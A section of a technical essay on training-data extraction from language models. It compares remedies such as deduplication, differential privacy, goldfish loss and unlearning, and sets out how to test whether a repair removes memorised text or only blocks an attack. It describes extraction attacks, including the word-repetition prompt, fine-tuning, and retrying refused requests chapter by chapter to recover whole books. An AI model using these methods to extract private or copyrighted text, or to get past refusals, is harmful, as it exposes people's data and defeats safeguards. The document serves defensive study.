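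Descriptions of the ChatGPT case show how easily people confuse blocking an exploit with fixing the vulnerability. The Decoder wrote that the vulnerability "was mitigated", which could mean either. Breitenbach and Wood, who had just demonstrated the limits of one filter, wrote that OpenAI had confirmed their findings as vulnerabilities and "subsequently patched" them, although the change they had observed was a wider filter.

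Blocking an exploit also makes the remaining weakness harder for outsiders to study. The word-repetition prompt was briefly the best tool they had for measuring how much ChatGPT had memorised. After OpenAI added a filter, it could still run the prompt internally with the filter off, but outsiders had to find another attack or rely on what the company told them.

Developers can reduce these risks without delaying the block. They can let approved researchers test the model without the filter. They can also give each block a review date, which follows Souppaya and Scarfone's advice to schedule the removal of emergency measures. At the review, someone has to check whether a fix exists and which variants have appeared since the block was introduced. If there is no fix, the developer should keep the block, widen it where necessary, and tell customers that the model can still release memorised text.

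## Fixing the vulnerability

A fix for the ChatGPT leak has to deal with the text the model has memorised. Filters block some ways of extracting it, and Yona and colleagues' correction makes the model less likely to diverge, but neither removes the text from the weights. A developer can change the data before training, change how the model learns from it, or alter the finished weights. Only the last option helps a model already in use, and it has the weakest evidence.

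| Remedy | What it guarantees | Main cost | Can a deployed model receive it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Remove sensitive passages from the data | The model can't memorise them, provided the developer found every copy | Finding them, and losing some useful text | No |
| Remove duplicates | Nothing about any particular passage | Computing time | No |
| Differential privacy | A mathematical limit on the influence of each piece of text | A large loss of capability | Only for data added by later training |
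| Goldfish loss (skip some tokens in training) | Nothing, though long exact copies become very unlikely | Somewhat more training | Only for data added by later training |
| Unlearning | Nothing | Little computing, but possible damage to other abilities | Yes |
| Retrain without the passages | The same as removing them at the start | A whole new training run | No, a new model replaces it |

### Removing sensitive text and duplicates

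The surest remedy is to keep a passage out of the training data. *Extractable Memorization From First Principles* (2026) points out that a model can't memorise text it wasn't trained on. It also counts near-copies as training data, because the content is the same even if the spacing or punctuation differs. A developer who deletes a web page with somebody's address therefore has to find and delete the reformatted copies too.

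*Apertus* (Hernández-Cano, Hägele et al., 2025) describes how a Swiss project prepared the training data for two open models, with 8 billion and 70 billion weights. The team filtered out personal information and pages whose owners had opted out of collection by AI companies. They also applied the opt-outs in force in January 2025 to pages that others had collected earlier. They did this before training because anyone who downloads an open model can train away its refusals.

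A filter removes only the personal information it detects. Phone numbers and email addresses have a typical form, but a sentence saying which neighbour is in hospital doesn't. Deleting every page that mentions a private person would remove more personal information, but also a great deal of harmless text.

Removing duplicates is easier to automate, and it helps because models are more likely to memorise text they see often. The best-known evidence is *Deduplicating Training Data Makes Language Models Better* (2021), which found that deleting exact repeated strings reduced verbatim memorisation about tenfold, according to the summary in *Merlin* (2026). *Deduplicating Training Data Mitigates Privacy Risks in Language Models* (2022) tested the effect on privacy attacks, and the survey *Beyond the Black Box* (2026) reports that retraining models on data without repeated sequences greatly reduced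 the risk from these attacks.

The 2023 results from Nasr and colleagues seem to contradict this. They compared two Pythia models with versions trained on deduplicated data, generating a billion tokens from each:

| Model | Share of output in memorised passages | Different 50-token sequences found | Estimated minimum total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pythia 1.4B | 0.453% | 811,384 | 4,366,732 |
| Pythia 1.4B, deduplicated | 0.578% | 837,582 | 4,147,688 |
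| Pythia 6.9B | 0.548% | 1,281,172 | 6,762,021 |
| Pythia 6.9B, deduplicated | 0.596% | 1,313,758 | 6,761,831 |

The deduplicated models produced slightly more memorised text at both sizes, but the estimated total fell by 5% for the smaller model and hardly changed for the larger one.

Both sets of results can be right, partly because the developers removed duplicates in different ways. *Quantifying Memorization Across Neural Language Models* (2022) describes one of the 2021 models, whose developers removed every 50-token string that occurred more than once in the training data. Nasr and colleagues use the same length in their test for memorisation, so this method removed exactly the kind of repetition that the test detects. They attribute the weak result for Pythia to a coarser method. For example, a program that only compares whole documents will miss a software licence repeated at the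 foot of thousands of otherwise different pages.

Coarse deduplication can't be the whole explanation, though. In the 2022 study, a model whose developers had removed only near-duplicate documents still memorised less than the original. The number of passes over the data probably matters too. *Towards More Realistic Extraction Attacks* (More, Ganesh and Farnadi, 2024) notes that the standard Pythia models went through their data once. The deduplicated models trained for the same number of steps on a smaller dataset, so they went through it about one and a half times. If deduplication worked perfectly, a passage with 100 copies would appear about 1.5 times in training instead of 100, but a passage with a single copy would appear about 1.5 times instead of once. The deduplicated models may therefore have memorised less of the most repeated text and slightly more of everything else.

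The studies also measured different things. Nasr and colleagues counted memorised text in whatever the models wrote after a short, unrelated prompt. More and colleagues gave the models 50 tokens of a training passage and checked whether they produced the next 50. By that measure, deduplicated Pythia did leak less than the standard version. But when the researchers combined the results of attacks with different prompts, model sizes and training snapshots, they extracted as much from the deduplicated models as the best single attack had from the standard ones.

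Deduplication is still worth doing. It usually improves a model, and *Beyond the Black Box* describes it as standard practice. According to *K2-V2* (2025), the developers of that open model removed about 17% of their documents as exact duplicates, then searched the remaining 40 billion for near-duplicates. Afterwards they repeated some documents on purpose. An outsider therefore can't tell from the label "deduplicated" how many times a model was trained on a particular page.

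Slightly altered copies are another difficulty, because they add about 0.8 times as much to memorisation as exact copies do, according to research that *Merlin* summarises. *Scale Dependent Data Duplication* (2026) finds that more capable models also learn much the same thing from documents that share a meaning but not a wording. That study is about the quality of the resulting model, not extraction, but ordinary deduplication would also miss a phone number that appears on ten differently worded pages, or on only one page.

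### Differential privacy

Differential privacy is the only one of these training methods that comes with a proof. Suppose a developer could train a model on two datasets that are identical except that one lacks a particular passage. Training involves chance, so either dataset could produce many different models. Differential privacy requires the following to hold for any result that someone might look for in the finished model:

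```
P(result, with the passage) ≤ e^ε × P(result, without it) + δ
```

The same must be true with the two datasets swapped. Epsilon (ε) limits how much the passage can change the odds, and a smaller value gives stronger protection. Delta (δ) is a small allowance on top of that limit.

Google's VaultGemma, an open model with a billion weights, is an example. *VaultGemma* (2025) reports an ε of at most 2 and a δ of at most 0.00000000011. Since e² is about 7.4, the probability of a result with the passage is at most about 7.4 times the probability without it, plus δ. Suppose a model that never saw someone's phone number would have a one in a billion chance of completing a sentence with it by luck. The probability for VaultGemma is then at most about 7.5 in a billion.

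The developers achieved this by changing each step of training:

1. For each sequence in a batch, the program calculates the change to the weights that would help the model predict that sequence.
2. It shrinks any change that exceeds a fixed size, so no sequence can have much effect.
3. It adds the changes together, adds random noise, and updates the weights with the average.

A pattern shared by many sequences adds up across the batch and stands out from the noise, but one person's phone number does not. This is why private training needs very large batches. Each VaultGemma batch contained about 518,000 sequences, and Google trained the model for 100,000 steps on 2,048 chips.

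The guarantee covers a sequence of 1,024 tokens, not a person or a fact. If the same text appears in several sequences, each one counts separately. Google's sampling could include a document up to seven times, although for most sources it was fewer than three. With seven copies, the general limit rises from e² to e¹⁴, or about 1.2 million, which is too high to be useful. The actual protection may be much better than this worst case, but that isn't proven. Differential privacy therefore works best after careful deduplication.

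A smaller δ would also have made the guarantee more convincing. The training data had 13 trillion tokens, or roughly 12.7 billion sequences, and multiplying the number of sequences by δ gives about 1.4. The definition alone would therefore permit a training method that completely exposed one or two random sequences, although adding noise doesn't fail in this all-or-nothing way.

Google also tested directly for memorisation by giving VaultGemma 50 tokens from each of about a million samples of its training text and comparing its continuations with the next 50 tokens. It found no continuations that matched exactly or differed by 10% or less. Every earlier Gemma model had shown some memorisation in this kind of test. The result is more persuasive than it would be for a chat model, because VaultGemma has had no alignment training that could hide memorised text.

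The cost in capability was high:

| Test | VaultGemma 1B | Gemma 3 1B | GPT-2 1.5B |
|---|---|---|---|
| ARC-E (school science questions) | 51.8 | 71.3 | 51.1 |
| HellaSwag (choosing a sensible continuation) | 39.1 | 61.0 | 47.9 |
| TriviaQA (general knowledge) | 11.2 | 39.8 | 6.0 |

Google concludes that private training now gives results comparable to ordinary models from about five years earlier. That slightly overstates the results on HellaSwag, where VaultGemma scores nine points below GPT-2, a model from 2019. The comparison with Gemma 3 somewhat exaggerates how much privacy reduces performance, because Gemma 3 also benefits from a newer training method.

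The loss is largest on factual questions, and this may be hard to avoid because the training program can't distinguish rare facts from private details, since both appear in only a few sequences. *The Privacy-Hallucination Tradeoff in Differentially Private Language Models* (Ramesh, Pruthi and colleagues, 2026) studied what happens to such facts by fine-tuning GPT-J, an open model with 6 billion weights, on about 20,000 Wikipedia articles. The fine-tuned model then wrote articles on AI topics too recent for its original training data.

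Before fine-tuning, 32.9% of the model's claims were correct, and ordinary fine-tuning raised this to 37.7%. With differential privacy, the figure was 33.8% at an ε of 16 and 31.6% at an ε of 8. The drop from 37.7% to 33.8% was not statistically significant, though human reviewers also found more unsupported claims in the private model's articles. The models replaced facts they had failed to learn with false ones. An ε of 16 gives almost no formal protection (e¹⁶ is about 8.9 million), so even a very weak guarantee may reduce accuracy somewhat.

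A company can't apply differential privacy to a model it has already trained. It can apply the technique when fine-tuning the model on new data, such as customer records, but the guarantee covers only the new data. *VaultGemma* warns that calling such a model "private" creates a false sense of security, because text from the original training remains exposed. Consistent with this, Ramesh and colleagues found that private fine-tuning made no significant difference to what GPT-J had learned earlier.

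### The goldfish loss

A method that takes less compute is to stop the model from learning some of the tokens in each passage. During training, a program calculates a loss, a measure of how badly the model predicted each token, and adjusts the model's weights to reduce it. *Be like a Goldfish, Don't Memorize!* (Hans, Wen and colleagues, 2024) proposed leaving a fraction of the tokens, such as one in four, out of the loss. The model still reads those tokens, but it never learns to predict them at that point in the passage.

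Suppose the training data contains the sentence "The porter keeps the spare key behind the boiler" and the program skips "boiler". The model may learn everything up to that word, but it then has to predict the next word without having learned it from this passage, and "door" is more likely than "boiler". A filter like MemFree, by contrast, only stops the model from outputting a word it has learned.

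The program has to skip the same tokens every time a passage appears, or the model will eventually learn the whole passage. Hans and colleagues therefore let the preceding 13 tokens determine whether the program skips the next one. The same 13 tokens always lead to the same decision, even if the passage appears on another website with different text around it.

Small chances of a wrong guess add up over a long passage. In Hans and colleagues' example, a model predicts each token it has learned with a probability of 0.999 and each skipped token with a probability of 0.95. If the program skips one token in three, the chance of an exact copy is:

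```
256 tokens, ordinary training:  0.999^256                 ≈ 77%
256 tokens, goldfish loss:      0.999^(171) × 0.95^(85)   ≈ 1%
 16 tokens, ordinary training:  0.999^16                  ≈ 98%
 16 tokens, goldfish loss:      0.999^(10.7) × 0.95^(5.3) ≈ 75%
```

The researchers tested this by training Llama 2 on 100 Wikipedia articles 100 times over. It memorised 84 of the articles with ordinary training and none with the goldfish loss. Partial copying remained with the goldfish loss, since the model's output overlapped with the originals about twice as much as that of a model that had never seen them.

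*Positional Fragility in LLMs* (2025) reports a larger-scale test of the method. An ordinary model with 8 billion weights reproduced most test passages almost completely after seeing them 128 times. Models trained with the goldfish loss, which skipped only 2% of tokens, reproduced less than 40% and did just as well on standard tests.

Hernández-Cano and colleagues then used the method to train both Apertus models on 15 trillion tokens. They planted passages from old books in the data, repeating some up to 128 times. The finished models reproduced these no better than passages they had never seen, even when the prompt contained up to 5,000 tokens of the original. The 22 exceptions, out of 10,672 planted passages, all came from famous texts such as Shakespeare's plays, the Bible and the US Constitution, which also appear in many versions across the web. A different line break was enough to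 change which tokens the program skipped, so the model could learn from one version the tokens skipped in another.

The goldfish loss is mainly a remedy for long verbatim copies, such as pages from a novel, and is less suitable for short personal details. If a phone number consists of four tokens and the program skips one token in four, the chance that it skips none of them is 32%. If it skips only 2% of tokens, the chance is 92%. A number that appears on several different pages is even less safe, because each page gives the program another set of preceding tokens. A developer therefore still has to filter out contact details.

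Hans and colleagues say the method "comes with no guarantees". Someone who already has a document can often still tell whether the model trained on it, which matters if the document is, say, a patient's file. The method requires a modest amount of extra training text. A model that skips a quarter of the tokens it reads has to read 26.7 billion to learn from 20 billion.

A developer can also use the goldfish loss when training an existing model further, but it protects only the new data. *Democratizing AI* (2025) tested this on models with 70 billion and 405 billion weights. Memorisation fell to about the level measured for text outside the experiment, but it rose slightly in the larger model as training went on. The researchers thought this model had probably memorised the skipped tokens during its original training.

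### Unlearning

Unlearning changes a finished model so that it behaves as if it had never seen certain text. A common method runs training in reverse, so that each step makes the model less likely to produce that text. This takes far less computing than training a new model, and the developer can install the result in a running service. If it worked reliably, it would be the obvious remedy for a leak like ChatGPT's.

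But most of the evidence suggests that it hides text more than it removes it. *SoK* (2025), a review of the field, concludes that current methods often "suppress rather than erase" what a model knows. Unusual prompts can bring the text back, and so can a small amount of further training on related, harmless material that doesn't contain the text. Using further training this way is much like the fine-tuning attack on GPT-3.5.

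*Probe-Geometry Alignment* (2026) describes a controlled test in which researchers edited the weights of a model to suppress a secret it had memorised. When they trained the edited versions on the secret again, it came back after one to three training steps, depending on which part of the model they had edited. This suggests that the edit had left most of the memory in place. A probe, a simple program that looks for information in a model's hidden states, could also still detect the secret perfectly. The retraining isn't a realistic attack, because anyone who can train a model on the secret already knows it.

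Newer methods try to remove this hidden trace as well. *Do LLMs Really Forget?* (2026) presents one called PARS and tests it by retraining the model on a small part of the removed text. Some of the text still came back, but the model's verbatim recall was 61% lower than with an earlier method designed to resist such retraining, and its recall of the facts was 19% lower.

Unlearning can also reveal what the developer wanted to hide. In *Extracting Forgotten Prompts from Targeted Unlearned Models* (2026), an attacker who could only send and receive text worked out which prompts the developer had targeted, because the model responded to them differently. Some models that scored well on ordinary tests of forgetting were still highly vulnerable to this attack. An attacker might therefore learn that a particular person had asked a developer to remove information.

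For now, it's safer to treat unlearning as a strong block. It may be enough for a hosted model that customers can't fine-tune, at least against attackers who use only ordinary prompts. It protects a model much less if the weights are public.

### Retraining or retiring the model

Retraining the model from scratch without the sensitive passages removes them, as long as the developer has found every copy. Anything less is unlikely to work. Nasr and colleagues note that models may eventually forget memorised text if they keep training on other data, but this can take several passes over that data, and later training is usually far shorter than the original run.

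Few companies will repeat a whole training run because of one leak. The Apertus project used up to 4,096 graphics processors at a time to train models that are small by commercial standards. But large developers regularly train new models anyway, so they can correct the data for the next model at little extra cost and keep the blocks on the old one until they retire it.

A newer model isn't necessarily safer. Memorisation declined from one ordinary Gemma model to the next, which Google attributes to changes in design and training, but it never reached zero. Retiring a model stops it from leaking memorised data only if the company controls every copy.

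### When no fix is affordable

A developer may have to keep a model running for months with the memorised text still in it, but it can at least avoid making the problem worse. If a bank wants its assistant to answer questions about accounts, it can have ordinary software check who is asking and then look up the relevant record, instead of training the model on customer records. The model then has access to the record only while answering, and the bank can correct or delete it later. Nasr and colleagues advised in 2023 against using language models for privacy-sensitive purposes "without extreme safeguards", and that advice still holds for models trained in the ordinary way.

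The developer can also narrow access, and retiring old versions is a good place to start because each version may leak different passages from its training data. More and colleagues tested this by prompting Pythia models with the text that came just before each of 2,000 personal details in their training data. The best single model completed 22% of the details. Attackers who could also use snapshots from other points in training would have obtained 33%. Commercial releases may differ more or less than these snapshots do, but keeping an old model online gives attackers another chance to extract data even after its successor has improved.

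The attacks on OpenAI's models showed that fine-tuning and detailed probabilities are also worth restricting. Request limits need to be low to have much effect. In September 2024, a $5 OpenAI account could send 3,500 requests a minute to GPT-3.5, or about five million a day.

Customers need to know what remains so that they can decide what to use the model for. With invented figures, a useful notice might read:

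> This model can reproduce passages from its training data, including some people's contact details. We block the prompts known to cause this, but the passages are still in the model. In our latest test, it completed 12 of 10,000 training passages. We will review this in March, or earlier if someone reports a new attack.

A notice like this is more useful to customers than a general warning that outputs may be inaccurate. Developers shouldn't use it as a reason to reject reports, because a new attack on a known weakness can show that the weakness is more serious than they thought.

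Someone in the company also has to decide to accept the remaining risk, and record the reasons and what would change the decision. In the PHP case, nothing prompted a review until there was an exploit. For memorised text, the company should review the decision if a new extraction method appears, or if it plans to offer fine-tuning or publish the weights.

The people whose details are in the model have no part in this decision. A developer can reasonably accept that a model will reproduce old poems, software licences, or even contact details that a business has published for its customers. But if a hospital has fine-tuned a model on patients' letters, a notice to the doctors who use it doesn't protect the patients. If the hospital can't remove the letters from the model, it should withdraw the model.

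## Testing whether a repair holds

After a repair, the developer has to find out whether it removed the weakness or only blocked the published attack. For example, if a repair has removed memorised passages from the model's weights, no variant of the attack should recover them, whichever layer of the product the tester attacks.

### A test procedure

The steps below apply to any repair of a deployed model, and the examples come from training-data extraction.

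1. Keep the original exploit as a regression test. Run it on every new version of the model and through every route customers can use, because a later change may undo the repair.
2. Vary one property of the attack at a time. For word repetition, the tester could change the number of tokens in the repeated phrase, then the number of repetitions, then the sampling settings. When a variant works, the tester knows which property the repair depended on.
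3. Hold back some variants from the people making the repair, so that they can't fit the repair to the test.
4. Test the base model, the aligned model and the full product separately.
5. Run the same attack on comparable text that the model has never seen, to find out how often it succeeds by guesswork.
6. Let someone who knows how the repair works try to defeat it, since defences that pass a fixed set of tests have often failed against such adaptive attacks.

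Varying a single property would have exposed the two-token gap in OpenAI's first filter, which resembles the gaps that incomplete software patches leave.

More and colleagues varied the prompts they used to extract text from Pythia. Longer prompts extracted more on average, but some passages came out only with shorter ones. Removing random words from inside a prompt made the attack much weaker, while adding random characters in front weakened it less and even released a few new passages. A tester should therefore keep the weaker variants and count a passage as exposed if any variant releases it.

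In the rapid-response experiments, a filter stopped familiar attacks more reliably than unseen variants, so a developer who tested only the familiar ones would have overestimated the filter. This is the case for holding some variants back from the repair team. Once the team has seen a held-back variant, it becomes an ordinary regression test, and the testers need a new one.

Testing each layer shows where a repair acts. If the base model still completes the passages and the aligned model doesn't, alignment training is hiding them. If the aligned model completes them and the product doesn't, a filter is probably responsible. The developer can also fine-tune a copy of the aligned model on ordinary documents and see whether the passages return, as they did with GPT-3.5.

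A full product can be less safe than the API beneath it. Ahmed and colleagues, who extracted books from commercial models, got the first four chapters of *The Great Gatsby* from the ChatGPT website but couldn't reliably do the same through OpenAI's API. A developer who tested only the API would have underestimated the leak.

### Extractable and discoverable memorisation

A tester who says that a passage no longer leaks has to specify which prompts that claim covers. Nasr and colleagues use two definitions. Let *X* be the training data, *x* a passage in it, and Gen(*p*) the text that the model generates from a prompt *p*.

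```
x is extractable if   Gen(p) = x  for some prompt p that an attacker
                                  can write without access to X
x is discoverable if  Gen(p) = x  where p is the text that comes
                                  just before x in X
```

The word-repetition attack shows that training text is extractable, meaning that an attacker can get the model to output it. Text is discoverable if the model completes a sentence from the training data when a developer supplies the first half. Researchers had often treated discoverable memorisation as an upper limit on what an attacker could extract, because they assumed no attacker would have better prompts than the training data.

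Nasr and colleagues checked this on GPT-Neo 6B, an open model with public training data. They searched several hundred billion tokens of the model's output, generated from short, unrelated prompts, for training sequences that earlier researchers had tested for discoverable memorisation.

| | Discoverable | Not discoverable |
|---|---|---|
| Extractable | 1,799 | 618 |
| Not extractable | 3,211 | 11,019 |

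Together, the two tests found 5,628 of the 16,647 sequences. Prompting with the preceding text found 5,010 of these (89%), and unrelated prompts found 2,417 (43%). The unrelated prompts extracted 618 sequences that had passed the first test as safe, about a quarter of their total, so discoverable memorisation isn't an upper limit on what can be extracted.

A developer checking particular passages, such as a list of phone numbers, should first prompt the model with the text that precedes each one, because this test is more sensitive and needs only one prompt per passage. Unrelated prompts show what an outsider without the training data could obtain. Neither test shows that the other 11,019 sequences are absent from the weights. The proportions apply only to this set. About 30% of it was discoverable, compared with roughly 1% of training data in earlier studies of many models, so it probably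 contained an unusual amount of repeated text.

### The probability that a passage comes out

Nasr and colleagues suspected that the discovery test missed the 618 sequences because it used greedy decoding, in which the system always picks the most likely next token. The same prompt then gives the same answer every time, so each passage either passes or fails. Commercial services usually pick tokens partly at random, so a user who asks again may get a different answer.

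*Measuring memorization in language models via probabilistic extraction* (Hayes, Swanberg and colleagues, 2024) gives an example in which Pythia 12B had to complete a passage of 50 tokens. The model ranked the correct token first at every position except the 37th, where the correct token ranked second. Greedy decoding took the wrong token there and never returned to the original text. With random sampling from the 40 most likely tokens, the model produced the whole passage 16.2% of the time.

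Their measure starts from the probability of the passage, *q*, which is the product of the probabilities of its tokens. A passage is (*n*, *p*)-discoverable if *n* independent attempts have at least a probability *p* of producing it once:

```
1 − (1 − q)^n ≥ p
```

For the passage above, *q* is 0.162, so an attacker needs 17 attempts for a 95% chance of success. A developer can calculate *q* without making those attempts, by running the model once over the known passage to get the probability of each token and then multiplying the probabilities together. Outsiders usually can't do this with a commercial model because its interface doesn't provide these probabilities.

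The two measures can differ greatly. Hayes and colleagues tested Pythia 2.8B on 10,000 Enron emails from its training data. The model completed 1.3% of them with greedy decoding and 9.04% with random sampling and enough attempts. The choice of measure can even reverse a comparison between models. Pythia 1B leaked more than GPT-Neo 1.3B under greedy decoding but less under repeated sampling.

This matters for repairs because a small change to the weights could make the most likely token the second most likely. The passage would then no longer appear in the greedy test, but anyone who asked a few times would still get it. But the greedy rate can overstate the danger when users make few requests. With Pythia 2.8B, it took more than 169 attempts per email before 1.3% of the emails were almost certain to be released.

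Exact matching also misses leaks. When More and colleagues accepted 500-token completions that were at least 95% similar to the original, they counted twice as many leaks. A repair that made the model change one word per page would score very well on an exact-match test without protecting anyone.

### Separating memorisation from guesswork

A measure can also count too many outputs as successes. *Extracting memorized pieces of (copyrighted) books from open-weight language models* (2025) points out that researchers who work with probabilities have to decide how high a probability counts as success. A capable model will sometimes complete a sentence correctly because the ending is obvious, even if it hasn't memorized the text.

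*Extractable Memorization From First Principles* proposes setting the threshold with matched controls, which are passages of the same kind that can't have been in the model's training data. In one experiment, OLMo 2 32B completed 7.54% of ten-token endings from Wikipedia entries in its training data and about 1.8% from comparable entries outside it, so roughly a quarter of the apparent leaks were probably just correct guesses.

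The proposed test gives every control a score, such as its probability under the model, and compares the suspected passage with them:

```
p-value = (1 + controls that score at least as high as the passage)
          / (1 + all controls)
```

With 99 controls, a passage that outscores all of them has a *p*-value of 1/100. The tester can then call it memorised with a false-positive rate of at most 1%. That rate applies to each passage separately, so a tester who checked 10,000 passages the model had never seen should expect up to 100 false alarms. The controls also have to be similar to the passage being tested. Comparing old news articles with new poems, for example, would reveal little about memorisation.

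For long passages, the thresholds are very low. A model that gave each of 50 tokens a probability of 0.3 would give the whole passage about 7 × 10⁻²⁷. In tests of Llama 3.1 70B on books, the threshold for 50 tokens ranged from 10⁻²⁷ to 10⁻²¹. A passage with a probability of 10⁻¹⁵ could therefore count as memorised even though nobody could make enough attempts to extract it. The paper calls a passage "extractable" only if it is memorised by this test and almost certain to come out within a realistic number of attempts.

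A repair can thus make text practically impossible to extract while leaving it in the weights. The paper also warns that a passage that scores below the threshold may still be in the weights, because a different prompt might give it a higher score. After a repair, a developer should check that the removed passages score no better than the controls on any of the tests.

A dispute in 2026 shows what can go wrong without controls. In *Alignment Whack-a-Mole* (2026), researchers fine-tuned three large models to expand plot summaries into prose. They reported that when the models were given summaries of books that weren't in the fine-tuning data, the output covered up to 85–90% of a book. In *Playing Whack-a-Mole with misconceptions about memorization, extraction, and copyright*, Cooper (2026) calls this measurement invalid. It counts any match of five or more words, far below the usual minimum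 of 50 tokens. The researchers generated about 100 times as much text as each book contained, which made short accidental matches more likely. The summaries could also reveal some of the book's wording. The researchers removed five-word overlaps with the prompt, but Cooper considers the risk of leakage serious and notes that they ran no control.

Cooper accepts that the longest matches, which run to hundreds of words, are real extraction. He has helped develop competing measures, so he isn't neutral, but anyone could test his objection by running the same procedure on a novel published after the models were trained. The study is good evidence that fine-tuning can release memorised passages, but until someone runs that test, it remains poor evidence of how much of a book is released. A developer who used five-word matches to test a repair might reject a repair that had worked.

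### Estimating what the test didn't find

Any test reveals only a sample of what a model has memorised. Nasr and colleagues compare estimating the total to counting fish in a lake. A researcher who marks and releases 100 fish, later catches 50 and finds marks on ten of them can estimate that the lake holds 100 × 50 / 10 = 500 fish. This assumes that every fish is equally easy to catch, but a model produces some memorised passages far more often than others.

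Good–Turing estimation allows for this by using how often each passage has appeared. In its simplest form, the chance that the next memorised output will be new is:

```
passages seen exactly once / all memorised outputs so far
```

If a tester has collected 200 memorised outputs and 120 of them are passages that appeared only once, the next memorised output has about a 60% chance of being new. A program can predict later outputs by using these probabilities to simulate the next one, adding it to the counts, and repeating. This method produced the estimated totals for Pythia in the previous section.

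Good–Turing gave better lower limits than the other methods Nasr and colleagues tried, but its estimates were still far too low when the sample was small. From a billion tokens of GPT-Neo 6B's output, it estimated about 3.6 million distinct memorised sequences. The researchers found more than 30 million after generating 500 times as much text. Small samples can also rank models in the wrong order. Pythia 1.4B released more distinct sequences than GPT-Neo 6B at first, but then slowed and fell behind. A developer comparing a model before and after a repair should therefore look at how quickly new passages keep appearing, as well as how many appeared in the first few hours.

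### What a clean result means

If the attack never succeeds, Good–Turing has nothing to work with. Suppose a tester makes 1,000 independent attempts and none releases memorised text. The true success rate, *q*, could still be above zero. The usual upper limit is the rate at which a clean result would have only a 5% chance of occurring:

```
(1 − q)^1000 = 0.05
q = 1 − 0.05^(1/1000) ≈ 0.003
```

The 95% upper limit is therefore about 0.3%, so an attacker making a million such attempts might succeed up to 3,000 times. The limit is roughly three divided by the number of clean attempts, so showing that the rate is below one in a million takes about three million clean attempts.

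A test of 1,000 requests can easily miss a rare failure. It took 5,179 attempts to make GPT-4.1 continue *Harry Potter*. If the true success rate was one in 5,179, a test of 1,000 requests had an 82% chance of finding nothing.

The attempts also have to be independent. If a system always gives the same answer to the same prompt, sending that prompt a thousand times counts as one attempt. Attempts all made in one afternoon may not be much more independent, because GPT-4.1 sometimes refused a request repeatedly and accepted the identical request later.

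An average can also hide the worst case. If the tester tries 1,000 randomly chosen passages once each, the 0.3% limit applies to the average success rate across all passages, and one person's address could still come out every time. Developers should test the most sensitive passages individually and, since they have the weights, calculate the probabilities directly. A test of 1,000 attempts would almost certainly miss a passage that comes out once in a million, but the calculation would reveal it.

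The limit applies only to the kind of attempt tested. Even if a thousand attempts with repeated single words fail, repeated phrases or fine-tuning might still work, and running more of the same test wouldn't rule that out.

### Whole books from commercial models

Ahmed and colleagues' study is useful evidence on whether memorisation persists behind safeguards newer than those of 2023. Between mid-August and mid-September 2025, they tested Claude 3.7 Sonnet, GPT-4.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Grok 3 on 13 books, 11 of them in copyright in the United States.

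Long copies contain small differences, so the researchers needed a measure that tolerated a changed comma without counting chance matches. Near-verbatim recall works as follows:

1. A program finds runs of identical words that occur in the same order in the book and the output.
2. It joins runs separated by no more than two words and discards anything shorter than 20 words.
3. It joins the remaining runs across gaps of up to ten words, if the gaps are similar in both texts, and discards anything shorter than 100 words.
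4. It adds up the matching words, leaving out the gaps, and divides by the length of the book.

For Claude and *Harry Potter and the Sorcerer's Stone*, this gives 76,001 / 82,382, or 92.3%. The study's headline figures for that book are slightly higher (95.8% for Claude) but show the same pattern.

| Book | Claude 3.7 Sonnet | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Grok 3 | GPT-4.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| *Harry Potter and the Sorcerer's Stone* | 92.3% | 74.0% | 69.0% | 3.9% |
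| *1984* | 95.5% | 5.9% | 9.6% | 3.6% |
| *The Great Gatsby* | 97.5% | 9.4% | 14.8% | – |
| *Frankenstein* | 94.3% | 2.4% | 1.5% | 2.0% |
| *The Hobbit* | 70.2% | 5.2% | 7.2% | 2.0% |
| *The Hunger Games* | 32.6% | 1.0% | 2.3% | 0.1% |
| *Catch-22* | 0.1% | 0.1% | 0.0% | – |

*Near-verbatim recall for seven of the books, calculated from the study's word counts; a dash means no result*

The variation between books matters as much as the high figures. A developer who had tested only *Catch-22* might have concluded that none of these models could recite a novel. Small percentages can also be a lot of text. GPT-4.1's 3.9% of *Harry Potter* is about 3,200 words.

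The low figures for GPT-4.1 are partly due to its refusal to continue past the first chapter. When the researchers gave it the opening of each chapter in turn and retried refused requests, they recovered more memorised text, which the refusals had blocked but not removed from the model.

The measure is more likely to miss copied text than to report copying that didn't happen, because it ignores passages that come out in the wrong order. As a control, the researchers used a novel published on 31 July 2025, after the models' training data ended. All four models failed to continue its opening, which supports the results, although it meant the researchers never asked for the rest of the book. The models also failed to continue *The Duchess War*, a novel from 2012, which shows again that a failure can't be used to tell whether a model saw a text in training.

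The study has other limits. The researchers chose most of the books because an open model had memorised them unusually well, so the results don't show how much of an average book a model can recite. They usually report only the run that extracted the most text, and they adjusted the settings for each model, so the results can't be used to rank the companies. Cost also limited the number of tests. The long series of requests to Claude for *Harry Potter* cost about $120, compared with $2.44 for Gemini. All four models are from 2025, so the study doesn't show how well their successors' safeguards work. It does show that two years after the word-repetition attack, commercial models still contained long memorised passages and their safeguards didn't reliably prevent their extraction.

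### Observations that point to a block or a fix

No single observation proves that a developer has removed a vulnerability, but some are much better evidence than others.

| Observation after the repair | Points to | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| The original prompt fails, but a variant with one property changed works | Block | The repair depends on a detail of the published attack |
| The product refuses, but the same model leaks through another route | Block | The repair is in a layer that the other route avoids |
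| The aligned model is clean, but the base model completes the passages as often as before | Block | The text is still in the weights |
| Fine-tuning on ordinary documents brings the passages back | Block | The repair made the text less likely to come out without removing it |
| The base model scores no better on the removed passages than on matched controls, and held-back variants and fine-tuning also fail | Fix | Several different tests found no trace of the text |
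| The developer has retrained the model without the passages and found no remaining copies in the data | Fix | A model can't memorise text it never saw, though the search may have missed altered copies |
| The original prompt fails 1,000 times, with no other tests | Neither | A filter, a refusal and a real fix would all give this result |
| The attack stops working after the company changes models | Neither | The new model may have memorised the same text |
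| The output still matches the training data, but only for a few words at a time | Neither | The matches may be common phrases |
| The model completes seen and unseen passages equally often | Neither | The test can't distinguish memory from guesswork |
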